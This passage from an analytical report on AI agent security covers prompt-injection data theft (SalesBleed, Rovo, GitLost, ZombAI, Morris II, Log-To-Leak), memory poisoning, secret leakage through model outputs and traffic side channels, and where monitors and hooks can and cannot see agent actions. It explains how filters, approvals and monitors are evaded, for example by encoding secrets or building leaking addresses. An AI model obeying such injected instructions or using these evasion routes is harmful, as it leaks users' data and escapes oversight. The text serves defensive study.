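SalesBleed affected Agentforce, the agents that Salesforce sells for handling customer records. *Vulnerabilities in Salesforce Agentforce Expose Wider AI Agent Risk* (Poireault, 2026) reports that the attacker needed no account and only had to fill in a public web form of the kind companies use to collect sales enquiries. The form's contents went into a customer record, and the instructions in them took effect when an agent processed that record. The agent then looked up company names and deal sizes and leaked them through DNS, which evaded Salesforce's filter for untrusted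 web addresses. The security firm Zenity reported the problem in June 2026, Salesforce closed the gap in the filter on 18 August, and Zenity published its findings in September.

A user can introduce an injection by uploading a file to Rovo, an agent that works across Atlassian's products. PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls* describes a user who uploads a guide found online and asks Rovo to organise some work tickets. Following instructions hidden in the guide, Rovo gathers tickets and internal documents, adds their contents to an address on the attacker's site and opens that address with its page-fetching tool, without asking for approval. Switching off web search for the whole organisation did not prevent this, because the page-fetching tool remained available. Rovo also displayed Markdown images, which gave attackers another way to extract data. PromptArmor,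 a security firm, told Atlassian about the flaws on 23 May 2026. It published in August, after more than two months of unanswered follow-ups, while the flaws were still open.

Microsoft and Salesforce both filtered outgoing addresses, but for each filter the researchers found a form of address it missed. According to PromptArmor, Rovo's tool would open any address the agent built. Limiting the tool to complete addresses already in the conversation would have blocked this attack, because Rovo had to build the address from the stolen data. An attacker might get around that limit by planting one address for each letter of the alphabet and having the agent open them in the order that spells out the secret.

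Like EchoLeak, SalesBleed and the Rovo attack were demonstrations by security firms, not known thefts.

### Log-To-Leak: theft through a logging tool

In the previous section's example, the search company could have poisoned the description of `search_docs` to obtain settings files. *Log-To-Leak* (Hu, Fan and colleagues, 2026) tested a similar attack that doesn't disrupt the user's task. The attacker runs an MCP server that offers an ordinary tool and a logging tool called `save_logs`. The ordinary tool's description contains an instruction with four parts: when to log, which tool to use, a reason such as compliance, and a statement that the step is mandatory.

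The harness puts this description in the prompt with those of all the other tools, so the instruction can affect tasks that have nothing to do with the attacker's server. Suppose the user asks about a private project on GitHub, a site for storing code. The agent gets the information from the GitHub server, then calls `save_logs` with the user's request, the GitHub server's name and reply, and the answer it is about to give. The user receives the answer as usual. The attack works only if the user has enabled both servers and the harness allows the extra call without separate approval.

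The researchers tried 555 requests with five servers and four models. GPT-5 could not produce valid tool calls for two of the servers. In the remaining 18 combinations of model and server, the agent made the logging call in 62.64% to 100% of runs, and 76.55% to 95.64% of the logged fields were accurate. The share of tasks completed changed by less than seven percentage points in 16 of these combinations and fell by about 20 points in the other two, GPT-5 with GitHub and GPT-5 with the map service Mapbox.

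The wording mattered a great deal for GPT-4o. On GitHub tasks, naming the logging tool succeeded at most 12.4% of the time, while the best version with all four parts succeeded 66.8% of the time. Claude Sonnet 4 made the call in over 99% of GitHub runs, even with a less structured prompt. The four models tested date from 2024 and 2025, and recent models resist other injections better, which suggests that the rates would now be lower. The attack also worked in two commercial products, Cursor with GPT-5.1 and Claude Desktop with Claude Sonnet 4.5, though the researchers did not measure how often.

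An instruction to keep a log for compliance is hard to filter because it looks much like a real company rule. One detector missed all 100 poisoned descriptions it examined. Another caught 91 of 100 but also flagged 85.53% of the harmless ones. Hu and colleagues recommend instead that the harness decide whether to authorise the additional calls such an instruction would trigger.

### Why a local model leaves the exits open

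Running the model on the laptop keeps the password from the model provider, but it doesn't stop an image request or tool call from leaking the password, because those happen after the model has produced its text.

Ollama, a popular program for running models locally, had this problem. PromptArmor's *Local models do not stop data exfiltration* explains that Ollama's chat window rendered raw HTML, the language of web pages, from the model's output, so an injection could make the model write an image tag that sent the user's uploaded documents to an outsider. The remedy is to change the window, for instance by showing HTML as plain text or blocking outside content.

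PromptArmor lists 20 flaws it found in commercial AI products, none of which depended on where the model ran. By its descriptions, nine involved an interface that displayed the model's output unsafely, and ten involved a failure in the step where a person approves an action. PromptArmor chose the cases from its own research and sells a service that watches for such flaws, so the list is a poor guide to how common each type is.

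### Secrets in harmless answers

A model can reveal a secret by avoiding it. Suppose a model is told to keep the number 47 private, and someone asks it for a list of random two-digit numbers. It will tend to leave out 47, and the gap becomes visible over many lists. Fairoze, Mangaokar and colleagues (2026) call this avoidance "suppression" in *Inadvertent Context Leakage in Language Models*, and they trained programs to exploit it.

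The researchers gave eight commercial models secret random numbers of one, two, four or eight digits and told them never to reveal them. All eight models refused direct requests. The researchers then made harmless requests, such as asking for a list of numbers, and trained decoders (mostly small language models) to guess the secret from the answers. They used 1,000 secrets for each combination of model and number length, and tested the decoders on secrets not used in training.

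The decoder recovered every two-digit secret from Claude Opus 4.6 and Gemini 3.1 Pro, and at least 94% of the digits from three other models. For four-digit secrets, it recovered the whole number 82% of the time from Claude Opus 4.6 and 44% of the time from Gemini 3.1 Pro. GPT-5.4 nano and Grok 4.1 Fast leaked much less at two digits and nothing measurable at four or more. These results are from the most successful combination of request and decoder for each model.

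The secrets were also very small. A four-digit number has 10,000 possible values, so identifying it takes log₂ 10,000, or about 13 bits. A random 40-character key made of letters and digits has 62⁴⁰, so identifying it takes 40 × log₂ 62, or about 238 bits, roughly 18 times as many. Accuracy was already falling at eight digits, where the best decoder got 41% of individual digits right, compared with 10% by chance. If each guess were independent, it would get all eight right less than once in a thousand tries. The experiment therefore does not show that whole API keys leak in this way.

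The attack also requires that the attacker know the length of the secret and that the prompt single it out as something to protect. The failing build meets neither condition. The password in its log was just another line of text, so the model had no particular reason to avoid it. Stronger warnings can increase leakage. On Claude Opus 4.6, the share of digits recovered rose from 5.4% with a one-line confidentiality instruction to 64.3% with a long, emphatic one, so leaving a PIN out of the prompt is safer than adding warnings to protect it.

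Personal facts can leak in a similar way. A trained classifier could use routine answers by Claude Opus 4.6 to predict, better than chance, whether a given fact about the user, such as a health condition, was in the model's context. It worked even for some facts that the answer never mentioned, but the test covered only one user's profile.

An attacker can use the same idea to steal data through an injection. Fairoze and colleagues gave a personal assistant a file containing a nine-digit US Social Security number, then injected an instruction to encode each digit as a number of exclamation marks. They recovered the full number in 52 of 70 trials with Claude Opus 4.6 and in 29 of 70 with Gemini 3.1 Pro. A filter that searched for the number would miss the encoded version. In all but one trial, however, Claude wrote the number in plain text before encoding it, which would have given the filter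 a better chance. The attacker chooses the code, so this method could presumably carry longer secrets, and the 13-bit comparison is not reassuring here.

### What encrypted traffic gives away

TLS hides the text of a message but not its size or timing. When a provider streams an answer token by token, a longer token usually makes a slightly larger packet, so someone watching the connection sees packet sizes and pauses that depend on the answer. Canale and Soulis cite an earlier attack that used token lengths alone to reconstruct 27% of an assistant's responses and infer the topic of 53%.

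Whisper Leak, an attack Microsoft researchers described in November 2025, uses both the size and timing of encrypted packets to infer the topic of a conversation. The researchers recorded encrypted answers to questions about the legality of money laundering and to many unrelated questions. They trained classifiers to tell the two apart and tested the method on 28 language models. The attacker never decrypts anything, and could be an internet provider or someone on the same wireless network.

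Rare topics are hard for any such classifier to detect without many false alarms. If one conversation in 10,000 concerns money laundering, a classifier that wrongly flags 1% of the others produces about 100 false alarms for every real case. For many of the models, the attack in Whisper Leak could avoid false alarms even when the topic was that rare by flagging only the clearest cases, and it still caught 5% to 20% of the target conversations. A government could use this to find some of the people asking about a banned subject. The paper found that providers can weaken the attack, but not stop it, by adding random padding to each piece of the answer or sending several tokens together.

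Traffic patterns can also identify the software in use. Canale and Soulis cite a system that recognised which agent had produced a traffic recording. It had an F1 score of 0.866 out of a maximum of 1, on a measure that penalises both misses and false alarms. Someone watching the failing build's traffic might learn which agent the developer uses and roughly what it is doing, but would not get the password this way.

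### Keeping credentials out of the model's context

A credential that never enters the prompt cannot leak from it. Many agents could use a credential without reading it, because a service like GitHub checks the credential when a request arrives and the model needs only the result. A credential vault stores the credential and adds it to the request after the request leaves the agent's control.

*API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary* (Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues, 2026) describes and tests one such product, Corvic Security Vault. The user stores a key in a connector, a record that also contains the address of the key's service. The agent sees only the connector's name. When the agent's code sends a request to that service, a trusted component outside the code's isolated environment adds the key as a header. Requests to any other address go out without the key.

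The vault passed all 16 of the researchers' checks. Code inside the environment made an authenticated request to GitHub but could not find the key in its settings, its files or its own copy of the request. Three outside services that send back whatever they receive returned no key, and a request to OpenAI while the GitHub connector was attached failed for lack of credentials. A second connector, for an economic data service, leaked nothing but did not work, because the vault put the key in a header and the service required it in the web address.

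All the researchers work for Corvic, which makes the vault, and they ran only 16 checks. They did not test redirects, in which an approved service forwards a request to another address, or attacks on the approved service itself. A vault also keeps many keys in one place, so a single breach could expose many of them. Kenney and colleagues mention a 2024 incident in which Hugging Face, a site that hosts AI models and applications, detected unauthorised access to secrets it stored for users.

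*Agent Authenticator* (2026) cites an analysis of 5,205 open-source MCP servers, of which 88% needed credentials and 53% relied on fixed keys or tokens. Only 8.5% used OAuth, a standard that lets a service issue limited tokens in place of a password. The keys are often stored in settings files that the agent, or any program it starts, can read.

Coding agents have simpler protections. The *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026) describes a setting that gives commands a placeholder when they try to read a credential. It also warns that a written instruction not to read secrets is "a preference, not enforcement". In the failing build, a placeholder would have kept the password out of the prompt, but a build step that needed the real password to reach the database would have failed. Corvic's vault would not have helped either if the build connected directly to the database, because the vault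 adds keys only to web requests.

Hiding a key from an agent does not limit what the agent can do with it. A prompt-injected agent with a GitHub connector could still publish private code if the key permits it. Kenney and colleagues rated eight threats by likelihood and impact, each on a scale of 1 to 5, and multiplied the two. They judged that the vault lowers the score for a secret pasted into a prompt from 25 to 4, but the score for a connector with excessive permissions only from 20 to 15. Customer records or emails that the agent retrieves through a connector also enter the prompt as ordinary text, and can leak by any of the routes described above.

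## Attacks made of several harmless-looking steps

An attack chain is a series of steps that do harm together, although each may look acceptable alone. A monitor that judges every message separately can approve each step and miss the attack.

Suppose a software company has an agent that answers public support tickets and can also read the company's private files. A stranger files a ticket about a failing export and asks whether other customers have had the same trouble and what the company did for them.

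| Step | What the agent does | Visible in the message alone | Visible to someone who knows the data's origin |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Reads the public ticket | A polite bug report with a reasonable question | A stranger's text, which will influence what the agent does next |
| 2 | Opens `export-cases.md` | A read of a file that the agent has permission to open | A private file, opened because a stranger asked about its subject |
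| 3 | Writes a summary: "Northwind Bank hit the same limit and moves to our new exporter in March" | Ordinary prose with no password or card number | Private facts about a customer, in new words |
| 4 | Posts the summary as a reply | A support answer sent to the company's own ticket site | Private facts on a page that the stranger can read |

A check for passwords or known attack phrases would find nothing in any row. It might catch the leak if someone had given it a list of confidential customer names, or if the agent had copied the file word for word.

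If Northwind Bank had announced its move in a press release and the agent had taken the same facts from there, the ticket, summary and reply could all be identical, but the reply would be harmless. A check that gives identical text the same verdict must either allow the leaking reply or block the harmless one. Most harnesses resend the whole conversation, so the evidence may well be in a single request, but the monitor still has to connect the reply to the file its facts came from.

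In July 2026 the firm Noma Security disclosed a real flaw that allowed almost exactly this kind of attack. Levi's *GitLost* describes how an attacker could post an issue (GitHub's word for a ticket) in an organisation's public repository and obtain data from its private ones. The agent was part of Agentic Workflows, a new GitHub feature. According to *GitHub Prompt Injection Exposed Private Repos via Issues* (Cross, 2026), it ran on Claude or Copilot, could read every repository in the organisation, and posted the private data as public comments. The attacker needed no credentials. By September nobody had reported a confirmed case of criminal use. The GitLost issues contained hidden instructions, so a good filter might have stopped them at step 1. The invented ticket would be harder to stop there because it contains only a question.

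### The lethal trifecta and the Rule of Two

*The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (Willison, 2025) names three capabilities that together let an attacker steal data: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate externally. The support agent is dangerous because it has all three, through its files, tickets and replies respectively. The failing-build agent also has them, through the settings file, the build log and the shell.

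Vendors usually respond to such attacks by blocking the route by which data leaves their own product. Willison notes that this doesn't protect users who combine tools themselves, which MCP encourages them to do. A ticket reader, a file reader and a tool for posting comments may each be safe until someone connects all three to one agent. A single tool server can also provide all three abilities. In May 2025 researchers showed that GitHub's official MCP server could read public issues, read private repositories and open pull requests (proposed code changes) that exposed the private data. GitLost followed the same pattern in another GitHub product 14 months later. Willison distrusts filters sold as catching 95% of attacks and advises users to avoid the combination entirely.

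Meta turned similar advice into a design rule. Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) allows an agent at most two of these properties within a session, meaning work done in one context window:

- **A:** it can process untrustworthy inputs.
- **B:** it can access sensitive systems or private data.
- **C:** it can change state or communicate externally.

An agent that needs all three must not act on its own. A person, or some other reliable check, has to supervise it.

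Property C is broader than Willison's third element because it also covers changing state, which includes deleting files and making payments. If an agent reads strangers' web pages and can wipe a company database but cannot send anything out, it avoids the lethal trifecta but still breaks the Rule of Two.

Meta's example is an email assistant that a hostile message could trick into forwarding the inbox. Its designer could let it read mail only from trusted senders, run it in a test environment without real data, or let it send only to trusted recipients unless a person has checked the draft. The support agent has fewer options because its job is to read strangers' tickets. The company could restrict it to public documents, but then the agent couldn't use what the company learned from past cases. Alternatively, an employee could approve each reply, but that helps only if the employee knows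 that the bank's move is confidential.

### Does removing one element always prevent theft?

An injection cannot steal data if designers completely remove the agent's access to sensitive data, its exposure to hostile instructions, or its means of sending data out. In practice, they often remove less than they think, and other kinds of harm remain possible.

External communication is the hardest element to remove completely, because images and DNS lookups can carry data as well as emails can. Lists of approved addresses also go out of date. *The Promptware Kill Chain* (Nassi, Schneier and Brodt, 2026) cites ForcedLeak, a 2025 attack on Salesforce's Agentforce. The attacker could buy an expired web domain for $5 and receive customer records there because the domain was still on Salesforce's approved list. An agent that cannot communicate externally can still delete files on an attacker's behalf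 or give its user a false answer.

Data can also leak through a second agent. Suppose one agent reads tickets and private files but can only write to an internal notebook, and another reads the notebook and posts public updates. Neither agent has the lethal trifecta if the second agent's designer treats the notebook as trusted, but together they can leak a private file. The Rule of Two covers this case if writing to the notebook counts as changing state, but most useful agents have property C under that strict reading.

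Removing untrusted content requires judging correctly whom to trust. Meta suggests that a coding agent with access to internal systems should filter its inputs by author. That would not help if an outsider took over a colleague's account, or if a colleague pasted a stranger's text into a trusted file. Accidental leaks could also still happen, since they don't require hostile text.

Meta slightly overstates its case when it argues that an injection has no meaningful impact without access to private data or sensitive systems. Its example is a research assistant that browses the web with limited access to private information "beyond the initial prompt", so whatever the user typed is still exposed. A hijacked browsing agent could also send spam or fill in forms on other people's sites. Meta says elsewhere in the document that the rule does not cover spam, agents' mistakes or misinformation in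 their answers.

An agent may change which two properties it has during a session. In Meta's example, it browses the web first, then permanently loses the ability to communicate before it opens internal systems. The loss has to be permanent because any hostile instruction from the web is still in the context window and could make the agent leak internal data if communication were restored. Even with communication disabled, the instruction could make the agent damage the internal systems if it can still edit them.

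The rule's last resort, human approval, works only if the approval step stays in place. The Hacker News (2026) examined a flaw in Claude for Chrome, Anthropic's browser assistant, that Manifold Security disclosed in July. Any other browser extension able to run a script on Claude's website could forge a user's click and start one of nine built-in tasks, including three that read the user's Gmail, latest Google Doc or calendar. By default, the user still had to approve the task before Claude read anything, but if the user had switched on "Act without asking", the task ran at once. The flaw was in Claude for Chrome's own code, so a model more resistant to prompt injection would not have fixed it. Anthropic had not released a patch as of 14 July. The approval step also gives little protection to users who click through such boxes by habit.

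### The promptware kill chain

Security analysts have long divided attacks into stages, and the best-known scheme is the Cyber Kill Chain, which the defence company Lockheed Martin published in 2011. Nassi and colleagues adapted it to what they call promptware, meaning text, images or other input that exploits the language model in an application and uses the application's permissions to do harm. Their first version, in January 2026, had five stages. A revision in February added reconnaissance and separated command and control from persistence.

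The table applies the seven stages to two of their cases. ChatGPT ZombAI demonstrated an attack on ChatGPT's memory feature. Morris II was a worm (a program that copies itself from victim to victim) that targeted email assistants.

| Stage | What it gives the attacker | ChatGPT ZombAI (October 2024) | Morris II (March 2024) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Initial access | Hostile text in the model's prompt | A web page that ChatGPT opened | An email |
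| Privilege escalation | Actions that the model's training or instructions should prevent | Text that overrode earlier instructions | A role-play jailbreak |
| Reconnaissance | Knowledge of the files, tools and data within reach | None | None |
| Persistence | Influence that outlasts one exchange | An entry in ChatGPT's memory | The email, stored where the assistant searches |
| Command and control | A way to send new instructions later | A web page that ChatGPT kept checking | None |
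| Lateral movement | Access to other users, agents or applications | None | Copies in outgoing emails |
| Actions on objective | The intended harm | Theft of user data | Theft of data, and spam |

Escalating privileges here means getting a language model to do things it can do but normally refuses to do. In ordinary computing, the term means moving from a limited account to a more powerful one, but a language model has no such accounts. An attacker can skip escalation when the model would carry out the request anyway, as the support agent did.

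Reconnaissance is also optional, because an attacker who knows the target application can write the instructions in advance. Otherwise, the attacker can have the model examine its own context and report what it finds, then choose the next step accordingly. Command and control requires persistence and an application that fetches text from the internet.

ZombAI relied on saved memories, which ChatGPT adds to every new conversation. After ChatGPT read the hostile page, it saved a memory telling it to visit a page on GitHub and follow the instructions there. The attacker could then change those instructions at any time without injecting anything again. A monitor that checked one of the later conversations would find ChatGPT opening a page on a well-known site, but the hostile page might not appear in that conversation.

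Morris II spread by exploiting how email assistants look up old messages. When a user asked for help with a draft, the assistant retrieved related emails, including a hostile one. Text in the hostile email made the model copy that text into the draft, and the recipient's assistant then stored the new email. The attacker needed to send only the first message. This persistence is weaker than ZombAI's because the text takes effect only when a search retrieves it, and newer emails gradually push it down the results.

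Nassi and colleagues apply the scheme to 36 incidents and studies from February 2023 to January 2026, without explaining how they chose them. Nassi co-authored three, including Morris II, and twelve are by the security researcher Johann Rehberger, who also built ZombAI. By their count, 22 of the 36 have at least four stages: none of the three from 2023, seven of the twelve from 2024 and 15 of the 21 since. No attack has more than five. The rise shows that researchers can now demonstrate longer chains, partly because products have gained memory and more tools. Most of the cases are demonstrations, so the rise is weak evidence of how often criminals use such chains.

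### A false memory planted by one email

*When Claws Remember but Do Not Tell* (Zhang, Zhao and colleagues, July 2026) measures how reliably an outsider can plant a false memory in personal assistants such as OpenClaw. The false memory could be that a supplier has a new bank account, for example. OpenClaw keeps its memory in text files and loads some of them into every session. The attacker sends one email and gets no feedback. The attack succeeds if the agent saves the false memory, its reply doesn't reveal this to the user, and the memory changes what the agent does in a later session.

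The researchers trained a language model to write these emails by practising on an imitation assistant. They then sent the emails through a real mail server, mixed with harmless messages. In 56 test cases, the attack succeeded 49 times against OpenClaw running GPT-5.4 and 40 times against an agent built with Anthropic's Claude Code and running Sonnet 4.6. It still worked against several kinds of defence.

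These rates somewhat overstate the attack's success. The researchers began with 200 candidate cases and kept the 108 in which inserting the false memory directly into OpenClaw with GPT-5.4 changed the agent's behaviour. The results therefore show how often an email can plant a memory already known to work on that setup. Both models also now have successors. Still, the attacker had only one attempt per case.

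A memory of this kind can get around the Rule of Two because the rule applies to one session at a time. The agent reads no email in the later session, so if its designer treats memory as trusted, the agent has only properties B and C and may pay the supplier without supervision. The designer could instead treat a memory as untrusted whenever the agent had read outside text before saving it, which requires a record of where each memory came from. But an assistant that reads email every day would soon have few trusted memories and would need approval for much of its work.

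### Does "kill chain" imply too much planning?

Some of the evidence doesn't fit well with the planned, start-to-finish campaign that the phrase suggests. Nassi and colleagues say EchoLeak, the email attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, had persistence because the hostile email stayed in the mailbox until Copilot retrieved it. They count Copilot's automatic mixing of that email with internal documents as privilege escalation. Both resulted from how Copilot normally works. Counted this way, many email injections will have four stages, even if they took little planning.

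The same steps can also happen without an attacker. Even if a real customer wrote the export ticket to ask an honest question, the agent still published Northwind Bank's plans. An investigator who assumed a kill chain might waste time looking for a culprit when the fault was in the agent's permissions.

The reply is that stages show where to interrupt an attack, whether or not anyone planned it. In *The Promptware Kill Chain*, an essay for the website Lawfare, Schneier, Brodt and colleagues (2026) argue that the model gives defenders a set of countermeasures. Harvard's Berkman Klein Center (2026) summarises their strategy as assuming that injections will get in and breaking the chain later, for instance by stopping them from persisting or by restricting the agent's actions. The support company could deny the agent private files while it handles a public ticket, or hold its replies for review.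 Either measure could stop the leak without anyone having to work out what the ticket's author intended.

This is a good argument for the model, but some stages are more worth blocking than others. The middle stages are optional, and 14 of the 36 attacks had only two or three stages in all. Blocking writes to memory would not have stopped an attack that never used memory. All 36 included initial access and a harmful final action. No filter reliably stops initial access, so a defender has the best chance of catching every attack at the final action, provided the monitor has enough information about the earlier steps to recognise it. Nassi and colleagues list seven kinds of defence for that stage, including sandboxing the agent's actions and checking each one against the user's goals. They also found that every defence strong enough to prevent an attack outright, at any stage, significantly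 reduces what the agent can do.

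## What a monitor can see from each position

A monitor's position largely determines whether it has enough information to recognise the last step of an attack. In the failing build, a monitor on the connection to the model provider could read the database password in request 2. But if a malicious package uploaded `build.env` during the build, it would open its own connection, and the monitor would not see the upload.

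### Plug-ins, sidecars, gateways and the kernel

An in-process plug-in is code that the harness loads and runs as part of itself. It can use whatever the harness has in memory, such as the tool call that is about to run. A sidecar is a separate process on the same machine as the agent or in the same deployment unit. A cloud gateway is a remote service that inspects the traffic of many agents.

A kernel monitor runs inside the operating system's kernel, the core program that other programs must go through to open a file, start a program or connect to a network. On Linux, such monitors often use eBPF, a way to run small, checked programs inside the kernel.

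The word "sidecar" comes from container design. A container packages a program with everything it needs and isolates it from other programs. *Design patterns for container-based distributed systems* (Burns and Oppenheimer, 2016) describes common ways of combining containers at Google. In its sidecar example, one container runs a web server, and a second collects the server's logs from a shared disk and sends them to storage. Separate teams can build and update the two containers, and the logging container works with any application that writes logs. A monitor in a sidecar has the same advantages, since its developers can update it without changing the agent.

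Burns and Oppenheimer call a container that relays the main container's communications an "ambassador". By their definitions, a "sidecar" that inspects an agent's traffic on its way out is an ambassador. The difference matters when the monitor fails. A web server keeps working if the sidecar that saves its logs crashes, but if a relay crashes, the agent either loses its connection or has to send its traffic around the relay without inspection.

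### Whose machine, and which traffic

"Local" and "sidecar" describe where a monitor runs, not what it can inspect. Two monitors on the same laptop may inspect entirely different traffic if one reads messages to the model and the other reads messages to tools.

The same monitor can also run in different places. *llm-fw*, a firewall for LLM traffic by the developer PIsberg, normally runs on the user's computer. One extra startup option makes it run on a shared server, where it inspects the model traffic of every computer that connects through it. It can read the same kinds of message in either place.

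A local monitor may also send the text elsewhere. Akto's *Sidecar Egress Proxy* describes a proxy that runs in the same group of containers as the agent on Kubernetes, a system for managing containers. Only containers in that group can connect to the proxy, but the proxy sends each prompt and response to a separate Akto installation, run by the customer or in the cloud, which decides whether to allow, rewrite or block the text.

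All of the agent's web traffic passes through this proxy, which decrypts only connections to listed AI providers (by default OpenAI, Anthropic and Amazon's Bedrock service) and forwards everything else unread. If the failing-build agent ran behind it, the proxy would forward the query to the search company without inspecting it.

### Redirecting the connection to the model

Because of TLS, a proxy can read messages to the model only if it becomes one end of the harness's connection. The simplest way is to change the address to which the harness sends its requests. In a setup documented by agentgateway, an open-source gateway, the user starts the program on the laptop and sets one variable:

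```
export ANTHROPIC_BASE_URL="http://localhost:4001/"
```

Claude Code then sends its requests to port 4001 on the same computer. They need no encryption for this step because it happens within the machine. The gateway reads each request, forwards it to Anthropic over TLS and passes back the reply.

Some of Claude Code's other traffic does not use this address. Anthropic provides further settings that turn this traffic off or let a company make the gateway the only destination allowed on the machines it manages. These settings apply only to the harness, so a script that the harness runs can still connect elsewhere.

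The other way is for a proxy to impersonate the provider with the computer owner's consent. In `llm-fw`, this takes four steps:

1. The setup program creates a certificate authority and adds it to the authorities that the computer trusts.
2. It sets a variable, `HTTPS_PROXY`, that tells programs to send their web connections through the proxy.
3. When the harness asks for `api.anthropic.com`, the proxy presents a certificate for that name, signed by its own authority. The harness accepts the certificate and encrypts its request to the proxy.
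4. The proxy decrypts and inspects the request. It then either returns an error or encrypts the request again and sends it to Anthropic.

The harness has to follow the proxy setting and trust the new authority. According to Anthropic, Claude Code normally trusts the authorities the operating system trusts, but many programs built on Node.js, a common system for running JavaScript, need a separate setting to do so.

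For programs that ignore the proxy setting, PIsberg has a mode in which the operating system redirects the providers' domain names to the local machine. This mode requires administrator rights and cannot cover services whose domain names vary by customer, such as Microsoft's Azure OpenAI, because the redirection needs each name in full. A program that is already running may keep its old direct connection until someone restarts it.

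### Tool proxies and harness hooks

An MCP proxy takes the place of a tool server in the harness's settings. For a remote server, the user enters the proxy's address, and the proxy forwards each call. For a server on the same machine, the proxy can start the server and pass messages between it and the harness. Either way, the proxy receives the tool's name and arguments before the server does and can refuse the call. In the failing build, an MCP proxy could read the query to `search_docs` but not the shell command, because the shell tool is part of the harness and doesn't use MCP.

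A hook is a checkpoint that the harness itself provides. Anthropic's *Hooks reference* explains how a user can have Claude Code consult another program before every tool call. For the first command in the failing build, that program would receive something like this:

```
{"tool_name": "Bash",
 "tool_input": {"command": "cat build.env; npm run build"}}
```

If the program returns "deny", Claude Code blocks the call and shows the model the reason. If it returns no decision, Claude Code applies its usual permission rules. The program can be a script or a service at a web address, including a sidecar on the same machine. Plug-ins can instead register functions that run inside Claude Code's process. Hooks also cover MCP tools and calls made by subagents, which are helper agents the main agent starts.

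A hook works only if the harness calls it and follows its decision. If a web service used as a hook fails, Claude Code lets the tool call go ahead by default, though a recent setting can make it block the call. Users can limit a hook to certain commands, but Anthropic describes this filter as best-effort and recommends the permission system for firm rules. The hook also receives only the text of the command, so `npm run build` looks the same whether or not the packages in the build are malicious.

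### AgentSight: reading text before encryption

AgentSight, the observation tool that reassembles streamed responses, reads the text of messages inside the harness's process, just before encryption or just after decryption, without being in their path. Most programs leave encryption to a library such as OpenSSL, whose functions `SSL_write` and `SSL_read` handle the readable text. AgentSight uses eBPF to attach probes to those functions, so it needs no proxy, certificate or changes to the harness.

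AgentSight also records kernel events, such as programs starting, files opening and connections to other machines. Zheng and colleagues use three kinds of evidence to connect these events with the model's responses:

- **Process lineage:** AgentSight tracks every program that the agent starts, and every program that those programs start. It discards events from unrelated programs inside the kernel.
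- **Timing:** An event shortly after a response may result from it. AgentSight uses a window of 100 to 500 milliseconds.
- **Argument matching:** A file name, web address or command in the response may reappear in a kernel event.

All three signals would link the model's first command in the failing build to the opening of `build.env`. If a package opened a connection three minutes into the build, only lineage would link it to the agent, because the time window would have closed and the address would not have appeared in any response. Zheng and colleagues say that together the signals definitively establish causes. That claim is too strong, because two events can occur within half a second of each other by coincidence, and lineage shows which agent a program belongs to but not which instruction led to it.

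In a prompt injection test of AgentSight, an agent was asked to download and build a project written in C. The project's README pointed to a web page with hidden instructions, and the agent followed them, sending the computer's list of user accounts to an outside server. AgentSight recorded the whole sequence, from the page request to the upload, and merged 521 events into 37. A second language model analyzed the merged events and rated an attack highly likely because the agent's actions did not fit its task.

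This shows that the combined record can contain enough to recognise an attack. However, it is a single case that the researchers created themselves, and they reported no false-alarm rate for ordinary builds. The analysis also explained the theft but ran too late to prevent it.

AgentSight slowed three programming tasks by 3.4%, 4.9% and 0.4%, a mean of 2.9%. The researchers ran each task only three times with the tool and three times without. The 4.9% slowdown was about one second, and response times from a remote model can easily vary by that much, so these results are better evidence that the slowdown is small than of its exact size.

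The encryption library is the weak point. Zheng and colleagues argued in 2025 that AgentSight relies on stable interfaces that an agent cannot avoid, and this holds for requests to the kernel. But eunomia's *Reverse Engineering Claude Code's SSL Traffic with eBPF* (2026), by the group that develops AgentSight, reports that AgentSight's standard probes captured nothing from a new version of Claude Code. Anthropic had changed how it packaged the program, which now contained its own encryption library without the labels that the probes used to find the right functions. AgentSight's developers restored the capture by comparing the program with a labelled public version of the software it was built on.

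A probe may also record no conversation because none took place. During one 60-second test, the developers captured only routine status messages and mistakenly concluded that Claude Code encrypted its conversations by a separate route. Nobody had sent a message during the test. eunomia also warns that the 512-kilobyte capture buffer may cut off large requests, which are common when a harness resends the whole history.

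By August 2026, AgentSight could find the library automatically in several popular agents, but its probes still required Linux and administrator rights. Zheng and colleagues say this method cannot trace agents built into editors such as Cursor. For those agents, AgentSight reads the session files they write about themselves, which may be incomplete.

### The failing build from five positions

The table compares what each kind of monitor could reveal about the failing build. The last column covers a hypothetical case in which one of the packages is malicious and sends data out on its own.

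| Monitor | Shell command | Password | Search query | Connection opened by a package |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Proxy on the model connection | Yes, before it runs | Yes, in request 2 | Yes, before the harness sends it | No |
| MCP proxy for `search_docs` | No | No, unless it is in the query | Yes | No |
| Hook before each tool call | Yes | No, because the command has not run yet | Yes | No |
| AgentSight | Yes, but cannot block it | Yes, in request 2 | Yes | Program and address |
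| Kernel monitor without text capture | Programs that start and files that open | No | No, only a connection to the search company | Program and address |

The three monitors that can read and refuse a tool call miss the package's connection. The kernel monitor detects it but cannot read the conversation that would help explain the connection.

### guardscope: 15 paths and eight designs

*guardscope* (Toyoda, Leung and U, 2026) lists 15 paths by which an agent's decision can take effect and eight designs for a monitoring system. For each design, it shows which paths cross an enforcement point, a place where the monitor can allow or deny an action before it takes effect.

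The first design has no monitor. Three place a gateway between the harness and its tool servers. The basic one handles only tools reached over HTTP, the next also blocks direct connections to the internet, and the third routes local tool servers through the gateway as well. Three more place checks in the harness. One uses the harness's own permission rules, another combines those rules with a gateway, and the third runs a policy engine inside the harness process. The eighth design works in the kernel.

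In the table, "yes" means the monitor checks actions on that path, and "no" means those actions bypass it. "Blocked" means something outside the monitor's policy, such as a network filter, stops the action. "Depends" means the outcome varies with the system's configuration. The three harness designs share a column because Toyoda and colleagues reported the same results for all three.

| Path | HTTP tool gateway | Plus blocked direct connections | Plus local tool servers | Checks in the harness | Kernel |
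|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Tool that works only in the harness's memory | No | No | No | Yes | No |
| File or network operation by the harness's own process | No | No | No | No | Yes |
| Program started by the harness | No | No | No | Yes | Yes |
| Program that keeps running after the tool call ends | No | No | No | No | Yes |
| Direct network connection | No | Blocked | Blocked | No | Yes |
| Connection through a helper on the same machine | No | No | No | No | Yes |
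| Tool server over HTTP | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Tool server over standard input and output | No | No | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Tool server over another local channel | No | No | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Tool that calls another tool server | Depends | Depends | Depends | No | Yes |
| Task handed to another agent | Depends | Depends | Depends | Depends | Yes |
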